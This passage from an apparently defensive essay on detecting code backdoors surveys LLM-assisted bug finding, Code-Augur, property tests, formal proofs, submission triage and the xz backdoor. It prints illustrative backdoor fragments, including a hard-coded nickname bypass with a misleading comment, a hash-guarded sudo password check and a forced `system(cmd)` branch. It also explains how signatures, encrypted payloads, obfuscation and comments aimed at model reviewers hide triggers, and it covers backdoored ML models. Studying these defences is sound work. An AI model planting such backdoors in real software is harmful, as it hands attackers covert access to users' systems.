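Help Net Security's *Anthropic's AI bug tests uncover previously undisclosed flaws* (2026) describes an experiment on this question that Anthropic published on 2 December 2026. The researchers collected 21 logic bugs disclosed between 2016 and 2026: nine in SQLite, eight in the image library image-png, and four in the compression programs zstd and Brotli. They gave Claude Mythos 5 the source code from before each fix, but not the fix.

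The model used four methods. In agentic code review, it explored the code, guessed which rules the code might break and proposed inputs that would break them. In an informal correctness proof, it tried to argue in words that the code always obeys its rules, so that a step it couldn't justify would point to a bug. The third method combined the model with a fuzzer, and the fourth combined it with a symbolic execution engine.

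In the blind setting the model had to infer the invariant from the code, while in the informed setting the researchers provided it. A bug counted as found if the model submitted an input on which the patched and unpatched versions gave different results. The model had three runs per bug and could submit up to 1,000 inputs in each run.

| Method | Blind, of 21 | Informed, of 21 |
|---|---|---|
| Agentic code review | 11 | 20 |
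| Informal correctness proof | 8 | 21 |
| Fuzzing with a model's help | 0 | 1 |
| Symbolic execution driven by a model | 0 | 2 |

When the model was told which invariant to check, its score nearly doubled for code review and more than doubled for proofs, and it almost always found an input that broke the invariant. Most of the difficulty was in guessing the invariant, which Anthropic's researchers name as the remaining challenge.

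Both search methods scored zero in the blind setting, which is unsurprising because without a rule neither can tell a wrong answer from a right one. Their scores in the informed setting are stronger evidence against them. Fuzzing found only one bug even with the rule supplied, so the lack of a rule can't be the whole explanation. One likely reason is that developers had fuzzed some of these projects for years, leaving mostly bugs that fuzzers are bad at reaching. A benchmark of old bugs in well-tested software is harder for fuzzers than a fresh submission would be.

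The symbolic execution result has a different explanation, because in the informed trial the model found 13 of the bugs by reading the code before the engine ran. The engine confirmed two of them. A project that accepted only confirmed bugs would have rejected the other 11, which were also correct.

The scoring was generous: the model could submit 1,000 inputs with no penalty for useless ones, and the researchers assumed that a successful input came from correct reasoning about the invariant. Because the patched version served as the oracle, the scores mainly measure how well the model generates a triggering input, and are weaker evidence of whether it could have picked that input out of its own list. The scores also exclude the 316 distinct bugs that the runs found beyond the original 21. Of those 316, maintainers had already fixed or knew about 189.

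Reading also found serious flaws that nobody had reported. In a separate round, code review found a flaw in Caliptra, a hardware security component, that could let a chip run unverified firmware. Informal proofs found more than 100 bugs in the part of the Linux kernel that checks whether small programs, written for a system called eBPF, are safe to run. As far as anyone knows, these flaws were all accidental, but the Caliptra flaw is the kind an attacker would want to plant.

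### Stronger models and remembered bugs

The researchers repeated the blind code review with nine models. Claude Sonnet 4.5 found one of the 21 bugs, Claude Opus 4.5 found five and Claude Mythos 5.2 found 15.

A model trained on public bug reports may simply remember some of these bugs, so the researchers asked each model about all 21 without showing it any code. Sonnet 4.5 and Opus 4.5 recalled none. Sonnet 5 claimed to recall three, but it claimed to recall invented bugs about as often. Opus 5 and later models recalled at least eight of the ten bugs disclosed through 2024 and at most one of the 11 disclosed later.

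Nine of the bugs were not recognised by any model, which makes them a fairer test. Sonnet 4.5 found none of the nine, Opus 4.5 found one and Mythos 5.2 found five. Subtracting these from the totals shows that Mythos 5.2 found 10 of the 12 bugs that at least one model recognised (83%), compared with 56% of the other nine.

Memory may explain part of that gap, but probably not all of it. Opus 4.5 recalled nothing, yet it found four of the twelve and only one of the nine, so the twelve may be easier. The numbers are small, but the rise from none to five on the unrecognised bugs is hard to attribute to memory and suggests that newer models read code better.

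### Code-Augur gives the fuzzer a rule to break

A model that reads a function and decides it is safe usually moves on, so nobody tests that decision. In *CODE-AUGUR* (Luo, Zafar and colleagues, 2026), a model that judges a piece of code secure must write the assumption behind that judgement into the source as an assertion. A fuzzer then searches for inputs that violate the assertion.

Their worked example is a flaw in Little CMS, a library that converts colours. A colour space implies a number of channels (red, green and blue make three), and a separate record of the pixel format also gives a number. The two must agree. The library checks that the colour models match, and a model reading that check would reasonably conclude that the numbers match as well. It would then add this line, written here in simplified form:

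```c
assert(fmt.channels == cs.channels);
```

But the check also accepts a wildcard format without comparing the numbers. A fuzzer can produce a colour profile with 13 channels in one place and one in the other, which makes the assertion fail. No memory error has happened yet, because the library has only stored two numbers. The error comes in a later call, which tries to read 13 channels from a four-byte buffer. A fuzzer is much more likely to break the assertion than to produce a profile that also reaches the later call.

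For some numeric rules, Code-Augur also measures how close each run came to breaking the rule. If a length must stay below a maximum, for example, an input that brings the length closer to the maximum counts as progress. This lets the fuzzer work gradually toward breaking the rule where ordinary coverage might show no change.

When an assertion fails, the model decides whether the code has a real flaw or the rule was too strict. If it decides the rule was too strict, it rewrites the rule and the fuzzer runs again.

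Luo and colleagues compared Code-Augur with both Claude Code (Anthropic's general coding agent) and Atlantis, which relies more heavily on fuzzing. They used 39 flaws from DARPA's AI Cyber Challenge and 24 recently disclosed ones, and also counted any new flaws the systems found. Code-Augur found more flaws than either. Its smallest lead was 34%, over Claude Code on the competition's programs, with both using Claude Sonnet 4.6. Its largest was 370%, over Atlantis on the recent flaws, where Atlantis found only ten in total using the cheaper open-weight model DeepSeek V4 Pro.

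With Claude Sonnet 4.6, Code-Augur reproduced 41 of the 63 known flaws and Claude Code reproduced 42. Code-Augur's higher total comes entirely from new flaws, of which it found 76 and Claude Code found 38.

The new flaws were also unevenly spread. Code-Augur found 37 of its 76 in four versions of gpsd, a program that reads GPS receivers, where Claude Code found none. Claude Code found 24 of its 38 in a single 3D-model library, where Code-Augur found four. Code-Augur's lead was spread more widely across the competition's programs. Counting the runs with either model, it found new flaws in 16 of 23 groups of tasks, compared with nine for Claude Code.

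Code-Augur also cost more, averaging about $45 per audit with Claude Sonnet 4.6, compared with $16 for Claude Code. Over the 36 audits, that was roughly $14 per flaw for Code-Augur and $7 for Claude Code. The comparison doesn't show whether three runs of Claude Code, for about the same money, would have found as many flaws as one run of Code-Augur.

The fuzzer did contribute, though. Of the 117 flaws that Code-Augur found with Claude Sonnet 4.6, 45 came from broken assertions, 18 from ordinary crashes during fuzzing and 54 from reading alone. These figures record which part of the system found each flaw, so the model might have found some of the 45 by reading if it had kept looking. In this test, the model that was better at reading code also got more out of the fuzzer. With DeepSeek, broken assertions accounted for 30% of the flaws instead of 38%, because that model struggled to keep setting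 and refining rules over a long audit.

### Why the two results differ

Fuzzing looks nearly useless in Anthropic's experiment and valuable in Code-Augur's, but the two experiments have little in common beyond the combination of a model and a fuzzer:

| | Anthropic | Code-Augur |
|---|---|---|
| Targets | 21 known logic bugs in four projects | 63 known flaws, plus any new ones |
| Sign of a bug | Patched and unpatched versions give different results | A crash or an alarm from a detector |
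| Model | Claude Mythos 5 | Claude Sonnet 4.6 or DeepSeek V4 Pro |
| Budget | Three runs per bug, up to 1,000 inputs in each | Four hours and up to $100 per task |
| Compared with | Three other methods using the same model | Claude Code and Atlantis |

The type of bug probably matters most. Nearly every bug counted in Code-Augur's benchmarks ends in a crash or an alarm, so the fuzzer already has a reliable oracle, and the model's assertions only need to guide it toward the bug. If the model writes a poor assertion, the fuzzer can still find the crash. A wrong answer from SQLite produces no crash, so detecting it depends on writing the right rule.

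The results also depend on which bugs are counted. Anthropic counted known bugs. Luo and colleagues found that Code-Augur did no better than Claude Code on known flaws, and if they had reported only that figure, their paper would have supported much the same conclusion as Anthropic's. Fuzzing seems most useful for finding flaws that a reader would not think to look for, and counting known bugs can't measure that well.

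Claude Mythos 5 is also a much stronger model than either of those in Code-Augur. A stronger model finds more flaws by reading the code, which leaves fewer for the fuzzer to find, and nobody has published a test of Code-Augur's method with a model as strong. The V8 comparison is the nearest substitute because it used a current system on hard, heavily tested code. In that comparison, the fuzzer still found flaws that the model missed.

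Code-Augur did find logic flaws in a further test on real projects, where a finding didn't have to crash the program. Two were in chisel, a program for tunnelling network traffic. In one, chisel compared an address with a list of permitted patterns but didn't require the pattern to match the whole address, so it could accept a longer address that contained a permitted one. The planted filter that accepts "notexample.com" has almost the same flaw. People had to check each of these findings by hand.

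### Property-based tests as a middle way

Property-based testing is an older technique that divides the work similarly. A developer writes a rule, called a property, that a function should obey and describes the inputs it accepts, and a tool generates random inputs to look for one that breaks the rule. The auction site's invariant, that sorted bids must be in order with none missing, is a typical property.

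*Agentic Property-Based Testing* (Maaz, DeVoe and colleagues, 2025) had a language model write the rules. The agent reads a Python module and its documentation, proposes properties, then writes and runs the tests. It checks whether a failure comes from the code or the test, and whether a passing test could have failed. In one run, it found that it had wrapped a whole test in code that suppressed every error. After it removed the wrapper, the test failed and exposed a bug.

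Some of the rules were simple. Samples from the Wald distribution must be positive, but the numerical library NumPy sometimes returned negative ones. Splitting a dictionary into pieces and joining them again should give back the original, but a function in a toolkit for Amazon's cloud returned the first piece over and over. Neither bug crashed the program, and someone reading the code could easily miss the first because it came from rounding errors in a formula.

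In *Finding bugs across the Python ecosystem with Claude and property-based testing*, an agent produced 984 bug reports on more than 100 packages. The team checked 50 of the reports by hand and found that 56% were real bugs and 32% were both real and worth reporting. Among the reports that a model scored highest, 86% were real bugs. These results are from Claude Opus 4.1, a 2025 model, and later models probably do better.

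One of the bugs that Maaz and colleagues reported turned out to be intended behavior. A function that calculates the date of Easter returned days that weren't Sundays, and the maintainers replied that this was deliberate because the function can use a different calendar. They acknowledge that when code relies on an unstated assumption, only its maintainers can decide which rule is correct.

These tests call a function directly, so the generator doesn't have to get an input through the rest of the program. The earlier test of `may_read`, which checks that the function refuses a user with no grants, is an example. But random generation alone would practically never produce "heron-41", so the project would have to run the test under a fuzzer that copies values from comparisons into its inputs.

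### Judging two patches without running them

In *Agentic Code Reasoning* (March 2026), Ugare and Chandra had models judge whether two patches were equivalent without running either one. The models' accuracy reached 93% on patches written by AI agents. A maintainer could use this method to check a submission that is supposed to leave behavior unchanged, such as a refactored function, when building and fuzzing both versions would take too long.

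Seven wrong answers in a hundred is a lot for this purpose, and the figure doesn't show how many were harmless patches judged different and how many were different patches judged equivalent. The meaning of "equivalent" matters even more. A backdoored patch and a clean one give the same results on every test the project has, so a model asked whether they pass the same tests would be correct to call them equivalent. The reviewer has to ask instead whether any input would make the two patches behave differently, and ask for that input, so that the answer can be checked by running both patches on it.

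### When the author wants to mislead the reader

Nearly all the bugs in these comparisons were accidental. The partial exception is the AI Cyber Challenge, whose organisers planted flaws in real projects. Claude Code reproduced 32 of the 39 planted flaws that Luo and colleagues used, and Code-Augur reproduced 33. The results are encouraging for finding planted memory errors, but the organisers designed those flaws to test tools, not to get past a suspicious reviewer. Luo and colleagues say they didn't evaluate Code-Augur against someone who plants a backdoor.

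An explicit trigger check should be easier to find by reading than the 21 logic bugs were. A comparison with a secret password looks odd even to a reader who hasn't worked out the program's rules. The blind score of 11 out of 21 therefore probably understates how often a model would notice such a check in a small commit.

Disguised flaws are another matter, because a model infers the rule from names, comments and code, and the attacker wrote all three. Suppose the planted line in `may_read` arrives with an explanation:

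```python
    # Nightly search index needs read access to all documents
    return user.nickname == "heron-41"
```

A model might infer from this that owners, users with a grant and the indexing account may read a document. The code follows that rule, so a fuzzer that checks for violations will find none, however long it runs. The attacker has in effect written the rule that the fuzzer uses as its oracle.

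The rule should come from a source the submitter doesn't control, such as the specification or the previous version of the code. A rule inferred from the old `may_read` allows only owners and users with a grant, so the assertion fails on "heron-41" regardless of the comment. Better reading can't fully replace running the code here, because a comment can mislead a model that reads the code but doesn't change what the program does.

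The same protection is needed when a model rewrites a rule that seems too strict. In gpsd, Code-Augur inferred that the number of visible satellites should never exceed 184, the size of an array. Some inputs broke that rule because of real bugs. Later, a legitimate receiver broke it by reporting up to 230 satellites, and the developers rightly enlarged the array. An attacker would want the project to treat a violation caused by a backdoor as another sign that the rule was out of date. Somebody other than the submitter should approve any change that weakens a rule.

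Rules that survive this process remain useful for later submissions. The first fix in gpsd stopped the reported memory error but protected only one of the many places that used the satellite count. The assertion still failed because the bad number was still in memory, where other code could use it. Further fixes over the next four months all helped restore the same rule. A project that keeps such assertions in its source can run them against every new submission, and should look closely at any submission that deletes one.

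A project can also use Anthropic's scoring method to check a code change, by comparing the new code with the previous version instead of a patched one. A model could read the change and propose 1,000 inputs, and a script could run both versions on them and compare the results. Someone would still have to sort out the intended differences, but the model would only have to include an input that triggers the backdoor, without working out what the code was meant to do.

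## Triggers that no search can reach, and what a clean run shows

Every method so far works only if someone other than the attacker can produce a triggering input. An attacker can use a little cryptography to make sure nobody else can produce one, even with the complete source code.

### One-way functions and digital signatures

A one-way function is easy to compute but practically impossible to reverse. SHA-256, a standard example, turns any input into a 32-byte value called a hash. A laptop can hash a password in about a microsecond, but nobody knows how to find an input with a given hash much faster than by guessing. An attacker can use this to hide the secret password in sudo:

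```c
sha256(password, strlen(password), digest);
if (memcmp(digest, STORED_HASH, 32) == 0)
    ret = AUTH_SUCCESS;
```

The program now contains the hash of the secret but not the secret. Copying the compared value and splitting the comparison both fail, as they did against the checksum trigger, and now 32 bytes have to match instead of four. At 10,000 runs a second, a search typically matches the first two bytes in ten minutes and the first four in a year.

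A symbolic execution engine can write down the exact condition for reaching the payload, but its constraint solver fails because solving that condition means reversing SHA-256. Path explosion isn't the obstacle, since SHA-256 performs the same steps on every password of a given length. A language model would recognise the function immediately but couldn't reverse it either.

A hash protects only a secret that is hard to guess. If the secret were still "let_me_in", a tester could hash a list of likely passwords and soon find it. Anyone who recorded the password when the attacker used it could also reuse it.

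A digital signature avoids both problems. The attacker generates two linked keys, keeps the private one and puts the public one in the program. He can sign any command with the private key. The program checks the signature with the public key, which isn't enough to sign a new command. If each signed command also includes the name of its target server, a recorded command won't work on any other server.

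### The xz backdoor

xz Utils is a set of compression tools, and many Linux programs load its library. The backdoor that attackers hid there in 2024 became active only when OpenSSH, the usual program for logging in to a server remotely, used the library, as Kokkonis and colleagues describe. The hidden code inspected certain login attempts for a command signed with the attacker's private key. If the signature was valid, it ran the command. Otherwise it handed the request to the genuine code, and the login continued normally.

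The signature scheme was Ed448, and the best known way to forge a signature takes roughly 2²²⁴ steps, or about 10⁴⁸ years at a trillion steps a second. The signature also covered the server's identity key, so a command recorded on one server would not work on another. No fuzzer could have produced a validly signed command, which is why xz is not in ROSARUM.

Fuzzing a build from the project's repository would have missed the backdoor even without the signature requirement. The attackers had disguised the malicious machine code as test files for the compression tools, and the script that extracted it was only in the release packages, so a library built from the repository did not contain the backdoor.

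Andres Freund, a database developer, found the backdoor because logins were using too much processor time. A failed login took about 0.8 seconds instead of 0.3. The hidden code caused the delay by doing extra work whenever the login program started, so he could trace the delay to the library without triggering the payload. A better-written backdoor might not have slowed anything down.

### Forcing the branch

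The attacker can keep the private key secret, but the program still has to check the signature, so the check must be somewhere in the code. A reader who finds it can ask why a compression library needs to verify signatures. The coverage record is another hint, because no test written without the private key can run the payload, however good the tests become. Many harmless lines also stay unexecuted, though.

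A tester can also examine the payload without the key, by replacing the check with a condition that is always true:

```c
if (1)    /* was: signature_ok(cmd, sig, PUBLIC_KEY) */
    system(cmd);
```

The altered program runs any command it receives, and an oracle that watches system calls will detect the shell. REDQUEEN forces checksum checks to pass in much the same way, then repairs the input so that it passes the real check. But a tester can't repair a signature, and so never gets an input that works on the original program.

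A tester can come close to triggering the original backdoor by replacing the attacker's public key with their own, then signing commands and running the rest of the code unchanged. The security researcher Anthony Weems did this after the xz backdoor was discovered and showed it executing his commands.

Forcing a branch can make legitimate code look like a backdoor. If a tester forces sudo's password check to succeed, anyone can become root, which shows only that the check is important. An automatic updater that installs whatever its developer has signed has the same structure as the xz backdoor, but users know about the updater and who controls its key. A maintainer should therefore ask who holds the private key, and refuse the submission if the submitter can't answer.

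One way around this defence is to keep the guard out of the code that people read. In xz it was machine code inside a supposed test file, so a reader of the C source would have found no signature check to question or force.

The attacker can also encrypt the payload with a key computed from the triggering input. Forcing the branch then makes the program decrypt the payload with the wrong key and execute gibberish. Gauss, spyware discovered in 2012, derived its key from the names of files and folders on the intended victim's computer. Kaspersky, the security company that found it, tried millions of combinations without success and asked the public for help. An open-source project has an easier task than Kaspersky did, because it can refuse any submission that decrypts a block of data and runs it, without knowing what the block contains.

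Programs that already use a lot of cryptography are harder to protect. If a server keeps a list of trusted public keys, an attacker can add one more. The existing code handles the new key like all the others, so the backdoor adds no branch for a tester to force and leaves no line unexecuted.

Finally, the attacker can obfuscate the program, rewriting it so that the guard dissolves into the surrounding calculations and no separate check remains.

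### How much a detector could ever do

No general procedure can decide whether a program has a hidden behaviour. Suppose one existed, and somebody gave it this function, where `other_program` can't open a shell itself:

```python
def handle(request):
    run(other_program)
    open_shell()
```

The shell opens only if `other_program` eventually finishes. A detector that was always right would therefore determine whether any given program finishes, and Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no procedure can do that for every program. In 1953 Henry Rice extended the result to every non-trivial question about what programs compute.

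This doesn't rule out useful detectors, because a detector can return "don't know" and a project can reject whatever the detector can't clear. Real servers also limit the length of requests and the time spent on each, so in principle one could try every possible request. But there are about 10²⁴¹ different requests of 100 bytes, so the practical question is what a detector can do in a reasonable time.

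Christiano, Hilton and colleagues (2024), in *Backdoor defense, learnability and obfuscation*, study this question as a game. They had machine-learning models in mind, but their main negative result concerns Boolean circuits, which are networks of simple logic gates. Any program with a limit on its input and running time has an equivalent circuit. The game has four steps:

1. The attacker chooses an original function *f*, which answers 0 or 1, and a distribution of inputs.
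2. A random draw from that distribution picks the trigger.
3. The attacker writes a backdoored function *f\**. It must disagree with *f* on the trigger, but on no more than a small fraction ε of inputs overall.
4. A coin toss decides whether the defender receives *f* with a random input, or *f\** with the trigger. The defender has to say which.

The defender's task is far easier than vetting a submission, because if there is a backdoor, the defender already has the triggering input and only has to recognise it. Guessing succeeds half the time.

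The attacker doesn't get to choose the trigger, because that would make defence impossible. Suppose *f* accepts only one password and *f\** accepts only a different one. If the attacker could pick both passwords, nothing would distinguish the original from the backdoored version.

With unlimited computing time, the defender can nearly always win if ε is small enough. The defender uses the function's answers on a batch of random inputs to predict what it should answer on the suspicious input. Each batch is small enough that it probably contains no altered answers. The defender repeats this with many batches, takes the majority vote of the predictions, and compares it with the function's actual answer. How small ε must be depends on how flexible the class of functions is. Christiano and colleagues measure flexibility by the VC dimension, the size of the largest set of inputs on which the class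 can produce every possible pattern of answers. The defender's chance of losing grows in proportion to this dimension times ε.

The result changes when the defender must be efficient, meaning that its running time grows only polynomially with the size of the input. Christiano and colleagues prove that, for circuits of polynomial size, no efficient defender can do noticeably better than guessing. The proof assumes that one-way functions and efficient indistinguishability obfuscation exist. This kind of obfuscation scrambles circuits so that nobody can efficiently tell which of two circuits with identical behaviour a scrambled copy came from.

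In the proof, the original is an obfuscated circuit whose answers look random to anyone without its key. The backdoored circuit contains a damaged key that works for every input except the trigger, and the wrong answer for the trigger is written in separately. The proof also uses an intermediate circuit, which has the same damaged key but the right answer written in.

The intermediate circuit behaves exactly like the original, so the obfuscation makes the two indistinguishable. The intermediate circuit differs from the backdoored one in a single hard-coded answer. Without the full key, the right answer looks like a random bit, so nobody can tell it from the wrong one. The defender therefore can't distinguish the original circuit from the backdoored one, even with the trigger.

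Christiano and colleagues point to a 2021 construction of indistinguishability obfuscation by Jain, Lin and Sahai, which relies on well-studied assumptions, though such methods have been far too slow for ordinary software. For a maintainer, it matters more that the theorem assumes the *original* program is already obfuscated, so it doesn't apply to a project that accepts only readable code. The theorem rules out an efficient detector for all code, but not one that works only on readable code.

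Their result on decision trees shows how much a simple structure can help the defender. A decision tree checks individual bits of the input, one at a time, until it reaches an answer. If all inputs are equally likely, only one in 2³⁰ reaches any particular answer that lies 30 checks deep. In a tree with 1,000 possible answers, at most about one random input in a million therefore needs 30 or more checks. A backdoor that changes the answer for very few inputs must involve such a deep path, in either the original or the altered tree. The defender can count the checks and reject an input that needed too many, which takes no longer than running the tree once.

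Christiano and colleagues also discuss a 2022 result by Goldwasser, Kim, Vaikuntanathan and Zamir, who used digital signatures to backdoor a machine-learning model. Someone who can run both the original and the backdoored model, but not look inside them, can't feasibly find any input on which the two differ. A signature check in ordinary code would likewise hide a backdoor from differential testing, even with a perfect reference version to compare against.

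### What a clean run rules out

If each run of a fuzzer independently triggers a fault with probability *p*, the chance that *n* runs all miss it is (1 − *p*)^*n*. This is about 5% when *p* is 3/*n*, because ln 0.05 ≈ −3. So if a fuzzer with a good oracle reports nothing after *n* runs, one can say with 95% confidence that *p* is below about 3/*n*, which statisticians call the rule of three.

After 100 million clean runs, the bound is 3 in 100 million. A random try matches an 8-byte secret with probability 1/256⁸, or about 5 in 10²⁰. That is more than 500 billion times smaller than the bound, so the clean runs don't rule out such a secret. Lowering the bound to that level would take about 175 million years at 10,000 runs a second. A modern fuzzer can copy a plain 8-byte constant, so these figures apply to secrets it can't copy, such as one behind a hash.

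The rule also assumes that every input comes independently from the same distribution. A coverage-guided fuzzer breaks this assumption, since it builds new inputs from the ones it has saved. Marcel Böhme, one of AFLGo's creators, proposed borrowing another estimate from ecology, where researchers want to know how many species they haven't yet seen. Turing and his colleague I. J. Good developed it while breaking German codes in the Second World War:

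P(next observation is something new) ≈ *f*₁ / *n*

Here *n* is the number of observations and *f*₁ is the number of species seen exactly once. If a biologist has caught 1,000 butterflies and 30 species appear only once among them, the next butterfly has about a 3% chance of belonging to a new species. In fuzzing, we can treat each edge in the program as a species. If 50 edges have each appeared in only one of 100 million runs, the next run has about a one-in-two-million chance of reaching a new edge.

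Finding a new bug usually means reaching new code, so this figure is a rough upper limit on the chance that the next run finds one. Böhme, Liyanage and Wüstholz showed in 2021 that the standard estimates are much too optimistic for coverage-guided fuzzing, and they proposed estimators that correct for this bias. The bias arises because each saved seed can make later discoveries more likely, so the chance of finding a particular bug may rise during the search.

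Even a perfect estimate of this kind wouldn't rule out a backdoor. It adds up the probabilities of everything the fuzzer hasn't reached, and a branch behind an 8-byte secret adds only 5 in 10²⁰ to the total. An attacker who knows the secret can therefore open a shell with one request, even if the estimate is correct that the fuzzer's next million inputs will find nothing.

The bound is useful for accidental bugs. If the test inputs resemble real ones, a bug that affects fewer than 3 in 100 million of them will seldom trouble an ordinary user. But the rule of three limits only how often the fuzzer would send the trigger, not how often an attacker will, because an attacker doesn't draw requests from the same distribution.

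Tests on planted backdoors are a better guide to what a clean run means. Suppose one submission in 1,000 contains a backdoor that changes the system calls. Suppose also that 80% of these backdoors have triggers Lily would find in 90% of runs, and that the other 20% sit behind a signature. A clean run then lowers the risk from 1 in 1,000 to about 1 in 3,600:

0.001 × (0.8 × 0.1 + 0.2 × 1) = 0.00028

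About 71% of the remaining risk comes from the signed triggers. Running Lily many more times could bring the total down to 1 in 5,000 but no lower, because fuzzing can't reduce the signed part. The 80% is invented, and nobody knows the real proportion.

### Proof as an alternative

A proof can cover all possible inputs, including those that no search would generate. In formal verification, someone states precisely what a program must do, and a computer checks a proof that it always does so. This used to take years of expert work. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) describes a project with the verification company Theorem in which Claude proved security properties of the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries. According to Smith's *Claude Writes 180 Million Lines of Proofs to Verify 123 Open Source* (2026), the libraries all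 come from OSS-Fuzz, so fuzzers had already tested them.

According to RBC-Ukraine's *Скрытые ошибки в ПО*, a Russian-language news article, Claude turned each existing fuzz test into a mathematical statement that *no* permitted input makes the code crash. It proved such statements for 239 entry points, the places where a test calls into a library. The proofs total about 180 million lines, and a separate program, Rocq, checked them.

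Nobody has to read those lines or trust the model that wrote them. Kleppmann (2025) points out in *Prediction* that it doesn't matter if a model invents nonsense, because the proof checker will reject any invalid proof. Anyone can check a proof or a triggering input, regardless of where it came from.

The work also exposed bugs that testing had missed for years. One, in an image decoder, appeared only with about 64 MB of input and more than 2 GB of memory. Fuzzers would be unlikely to find it because they generally favour small inputs, which run faster.

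But Claude proved only that the code doesn't crash under the stated conditions, and the backdoored sudo doesn't crash. The same kind of proof would succeed on the planted `verify_user`, which doesn't crash under those conditions either. A proof eliminates search misses for the inputs it covers, but if the property it proves doesn't forbid the payload, the result is still an oracle miss.

A stronger rule would exclude this backdoor by requiring that `verify_user` return success only if `ctx->verify` did. The planted password breaks that rule, so there is no valid proof that the code follows it. The same is true if the attacker guards the payload with a signature, because a proof would have to cover the valid signature even though only he can produce it. The project can therefore block the backdoor by requiring a proof, without knowing the key.

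However, the project would not get a triggering input, and a failed proof may mean either that the code breaks the rule or that the model did not find a proof. A reader can still look at the place where the attempt got stuck, which in the planted function would be the branch after the signature check.

Somebody has to choose the rule, and Tolmach and Klaus (2026), in *The proof is in the spec*, argue that this choice has become the bottleneck as proofs get easier to produce. Their company sells verification, so they have an interest in saying so, but they are clearly right about backdoors. No short formula expresses "this program has no backdoor". The closest equivalent is a complete description of what the program may do, written by someone other than the submitter.

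The proof also has to cover the program that people run. Anthropic's proofs apply to single-threaded RISC-V programs in a simplified model of Linux, with all library code built into the program in advance. The xz backdoor redirected a function call while the system was loading a separate library, a step that a model like this leaves out. The proofs also don't cover code that the chosen entry points never reach.

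kirancodes.me's *who watches the watchers* tested these boundaries on lean-zip, a compression program with a proof that decompression exactly reverses compression. A Claude agent fuzzed it more than 105 million times and found no memory error in the verified code. It did find an overflow in the runtime of Lean, the language in which the program is written, and a way to crash or stall the archive parser, which nobody had verified. These flaws were accidental, but an attacker who knew what the proof covered would put a backdoor in one of the same places.

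When a submission isn't meant to change behaviour, such as a tidied-up function, the old version is a complete specification. A proof that the old and new functions give the same result on every input would rule out any new trigger that affects the result, even one that needs a valid cryptographic signature to fire.

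## Deciding which submissions get the expensive checks

Projects don't have enough computing time to fuzz every submission for a day and have a strong model audit it too. One way to choose is to give each submission a suspicion score, a quick estimate of how likely it is to be malicious, and run these slower checks on the submissions with high scores.

Kokkonis and colleagues' experiments give an idea of the costs. One ROSA run used eight processor cores for eight hours, or 64 core-hours. One Lily run used four cores for ten minutes, or about 0.7 core-hours. For a project with 50 submissions a day, that comes to:

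| Check on every submission | Core-hours a day | Cores in constant use |
|---|---|---|
| Lily | 33 | 1.4 |
| ROSA | 3,200 | 133 |

ROSA could stop early when it found a backdoor, but nearly all submissions are clean and would use the full eight hours.

*Automating Low-Risk Code Review at Meta* (Adams, Banga et al., 2026) describes RADAR, a system that reviews more than 25,000 code changes a day. Running ROSA on all of them would occupy about 67,000 cores, and running Lily would occupy about 700. Most projects could therefore use Lily on every submission their harnesses can run, but would have to ration any tool that needs as much computing power as ROSA.

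### Dividing four hours among three submissions

The US Navy had a similar problem in the Second World War, when it had too few ships and aircraft to search the whole ocean for submarines. *The Theory of Search* (Koopman, 1957) sets out the mathematics that came from its work on this problem.

Suppose submission *i* contains a backdoor with probability *p*ᵢ. If it does, *t*ᵢ hours of checking find the trigger with probability 1 − exp(−*a*ᵢ*t*ᵢ), where *a*ᵢ measures how fast the search works. With *a* = 1 per hour, one hour finds the trigger 63% of the time and two hours 86%. The project wants to divide its hours so as to maximise the expected number of backdoors found:

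Σ *p*ᵢ (1 − exp(−*a*ᵢ*t*ᵢ))

The marginal gain of submission *i* is the rate at which more time on it increases this sum, *p*ᵢ*a*ᵢexp(−*a*ᵢ*t*ᵢ). If one submission had a higher marginal gain than another that was getting time, moving a little time from the second to the first would increase the sum. So in the best plan, every submission that gets time has the same marginal gain. A submission gets no time if its marginal gain is below that level even at the start.

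Suppose a project has four hours to divide among three submissions, A, B and C, with probabilities 0.10, 0.01 and 0.001, and *a* is 1 per hour for each. A's marginal gain starts ten times as high as B's, so A gets all the time at first. After 2.3 hours (the natural logarithm of 10), A's gain has fallen to B's level. The two then share the remaining 1.7 hours equally, which gives A about 3.15 hours in total and B about 0.85. C gets no time because its marginal gain is only 0.001 backdoors per hour, while A's and B's are still 0.0043 when the four hours run out.

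| Plan | Backdoors found, in expectation |
|---|---|
| 3.15 hours on A, 0.85 on B | 0.101 |
| All four hours on A | 0.098 |
| Equal split | 0.082 |

The project doesn't have to know its budget in advance. Engler (1970) notes in *A Survey of Allocation Models in Search Theory* that when a search fails and the searcher gets more time, using the extra time optimally gives the same total allocation as planning for the full time from the start. C would get its first minute once the budget passed 6.9 hours.

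The best plan depends only on the ratios between the three probabilities. It would be the same if all three were a thousand times smaller, so scores that are far too high or too low for how common backdoors are can still be used to divide the time well if their ratios are about right.

The speed *a* matters as much as the suspicion. If a cryptographic signature guards the trigger, or the harness can't reach the new code, *a* is zero for a fuzzer, and the best plan is to give the submission no fuzzing time however suspicious it looks. It should go to a person instead or, if the harness is the problem, get a better harness first.

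The formula also assumes that a search finds the same fraction of the remaining backdoors in each interval, which Lily doesn't do. If Lily found 90% of the remaining backdoors every ten minutes, it would miss only one in a million after an hour. In the experiments, however, running it for up to an hour helped only slightly. If Lily finds nothing, a different kind of check is probably more useful than running Lily again.

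### What goes into a suspicion score

Most research on scoring code changes is about predicting accidents. Meta's Diff Risk Score, which RADAR uses, estimates how likely a change is to cause a failure in a live service. Adams and colleagues give the example of flagging 10% of changes and catching 60% of those that cause incidents. A flagged change would then be 13.5 times as likely to cause an incident as an unflagged change.

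*A Preliminary Study on Explaining Risk of Code Changes* (2026) gets a risk score by asking a language model whether a change could cause an outage and allowing only the answers 0 and 1. The score depends on the probability the model assigns to each answer, so each team can set its own thresholds for a warning, an extra review or a block. *DRS-OSS* (2025) offers open-source projects a free scorer that uses the commit message, the changed code and simple measurements of the change.

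Scores that predict accidental breakage may be poor at identifying malicious changes. A large change to a complicated service is likely to break something, but the backdoor in sudo is a single short `if` statement that breaks nothing. Low-risk changes at Meta can also skip human review, so an attacker whose change received a low score might avoid the people most likely to notice him. Meta reduces this risk by requiring a person to review any human-written change to its open-source code.

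A language model can check code for malice directly. *An Evaluation of Large Language Models for Detection of Malicious Python Packages* (2026) found that models caught most malicious packages but often flagged safe ones. Their average F1 scores, which combine missed packages and false alarms into one number with a maximum of 1, ranged from 0.40 to 0.99. Because the scores vary so much, a project should test its model before relying on it. Malicious packages tend to attack whoever installs them, which probably makes them easier to recognise than a backdoor that waits for a secret input.

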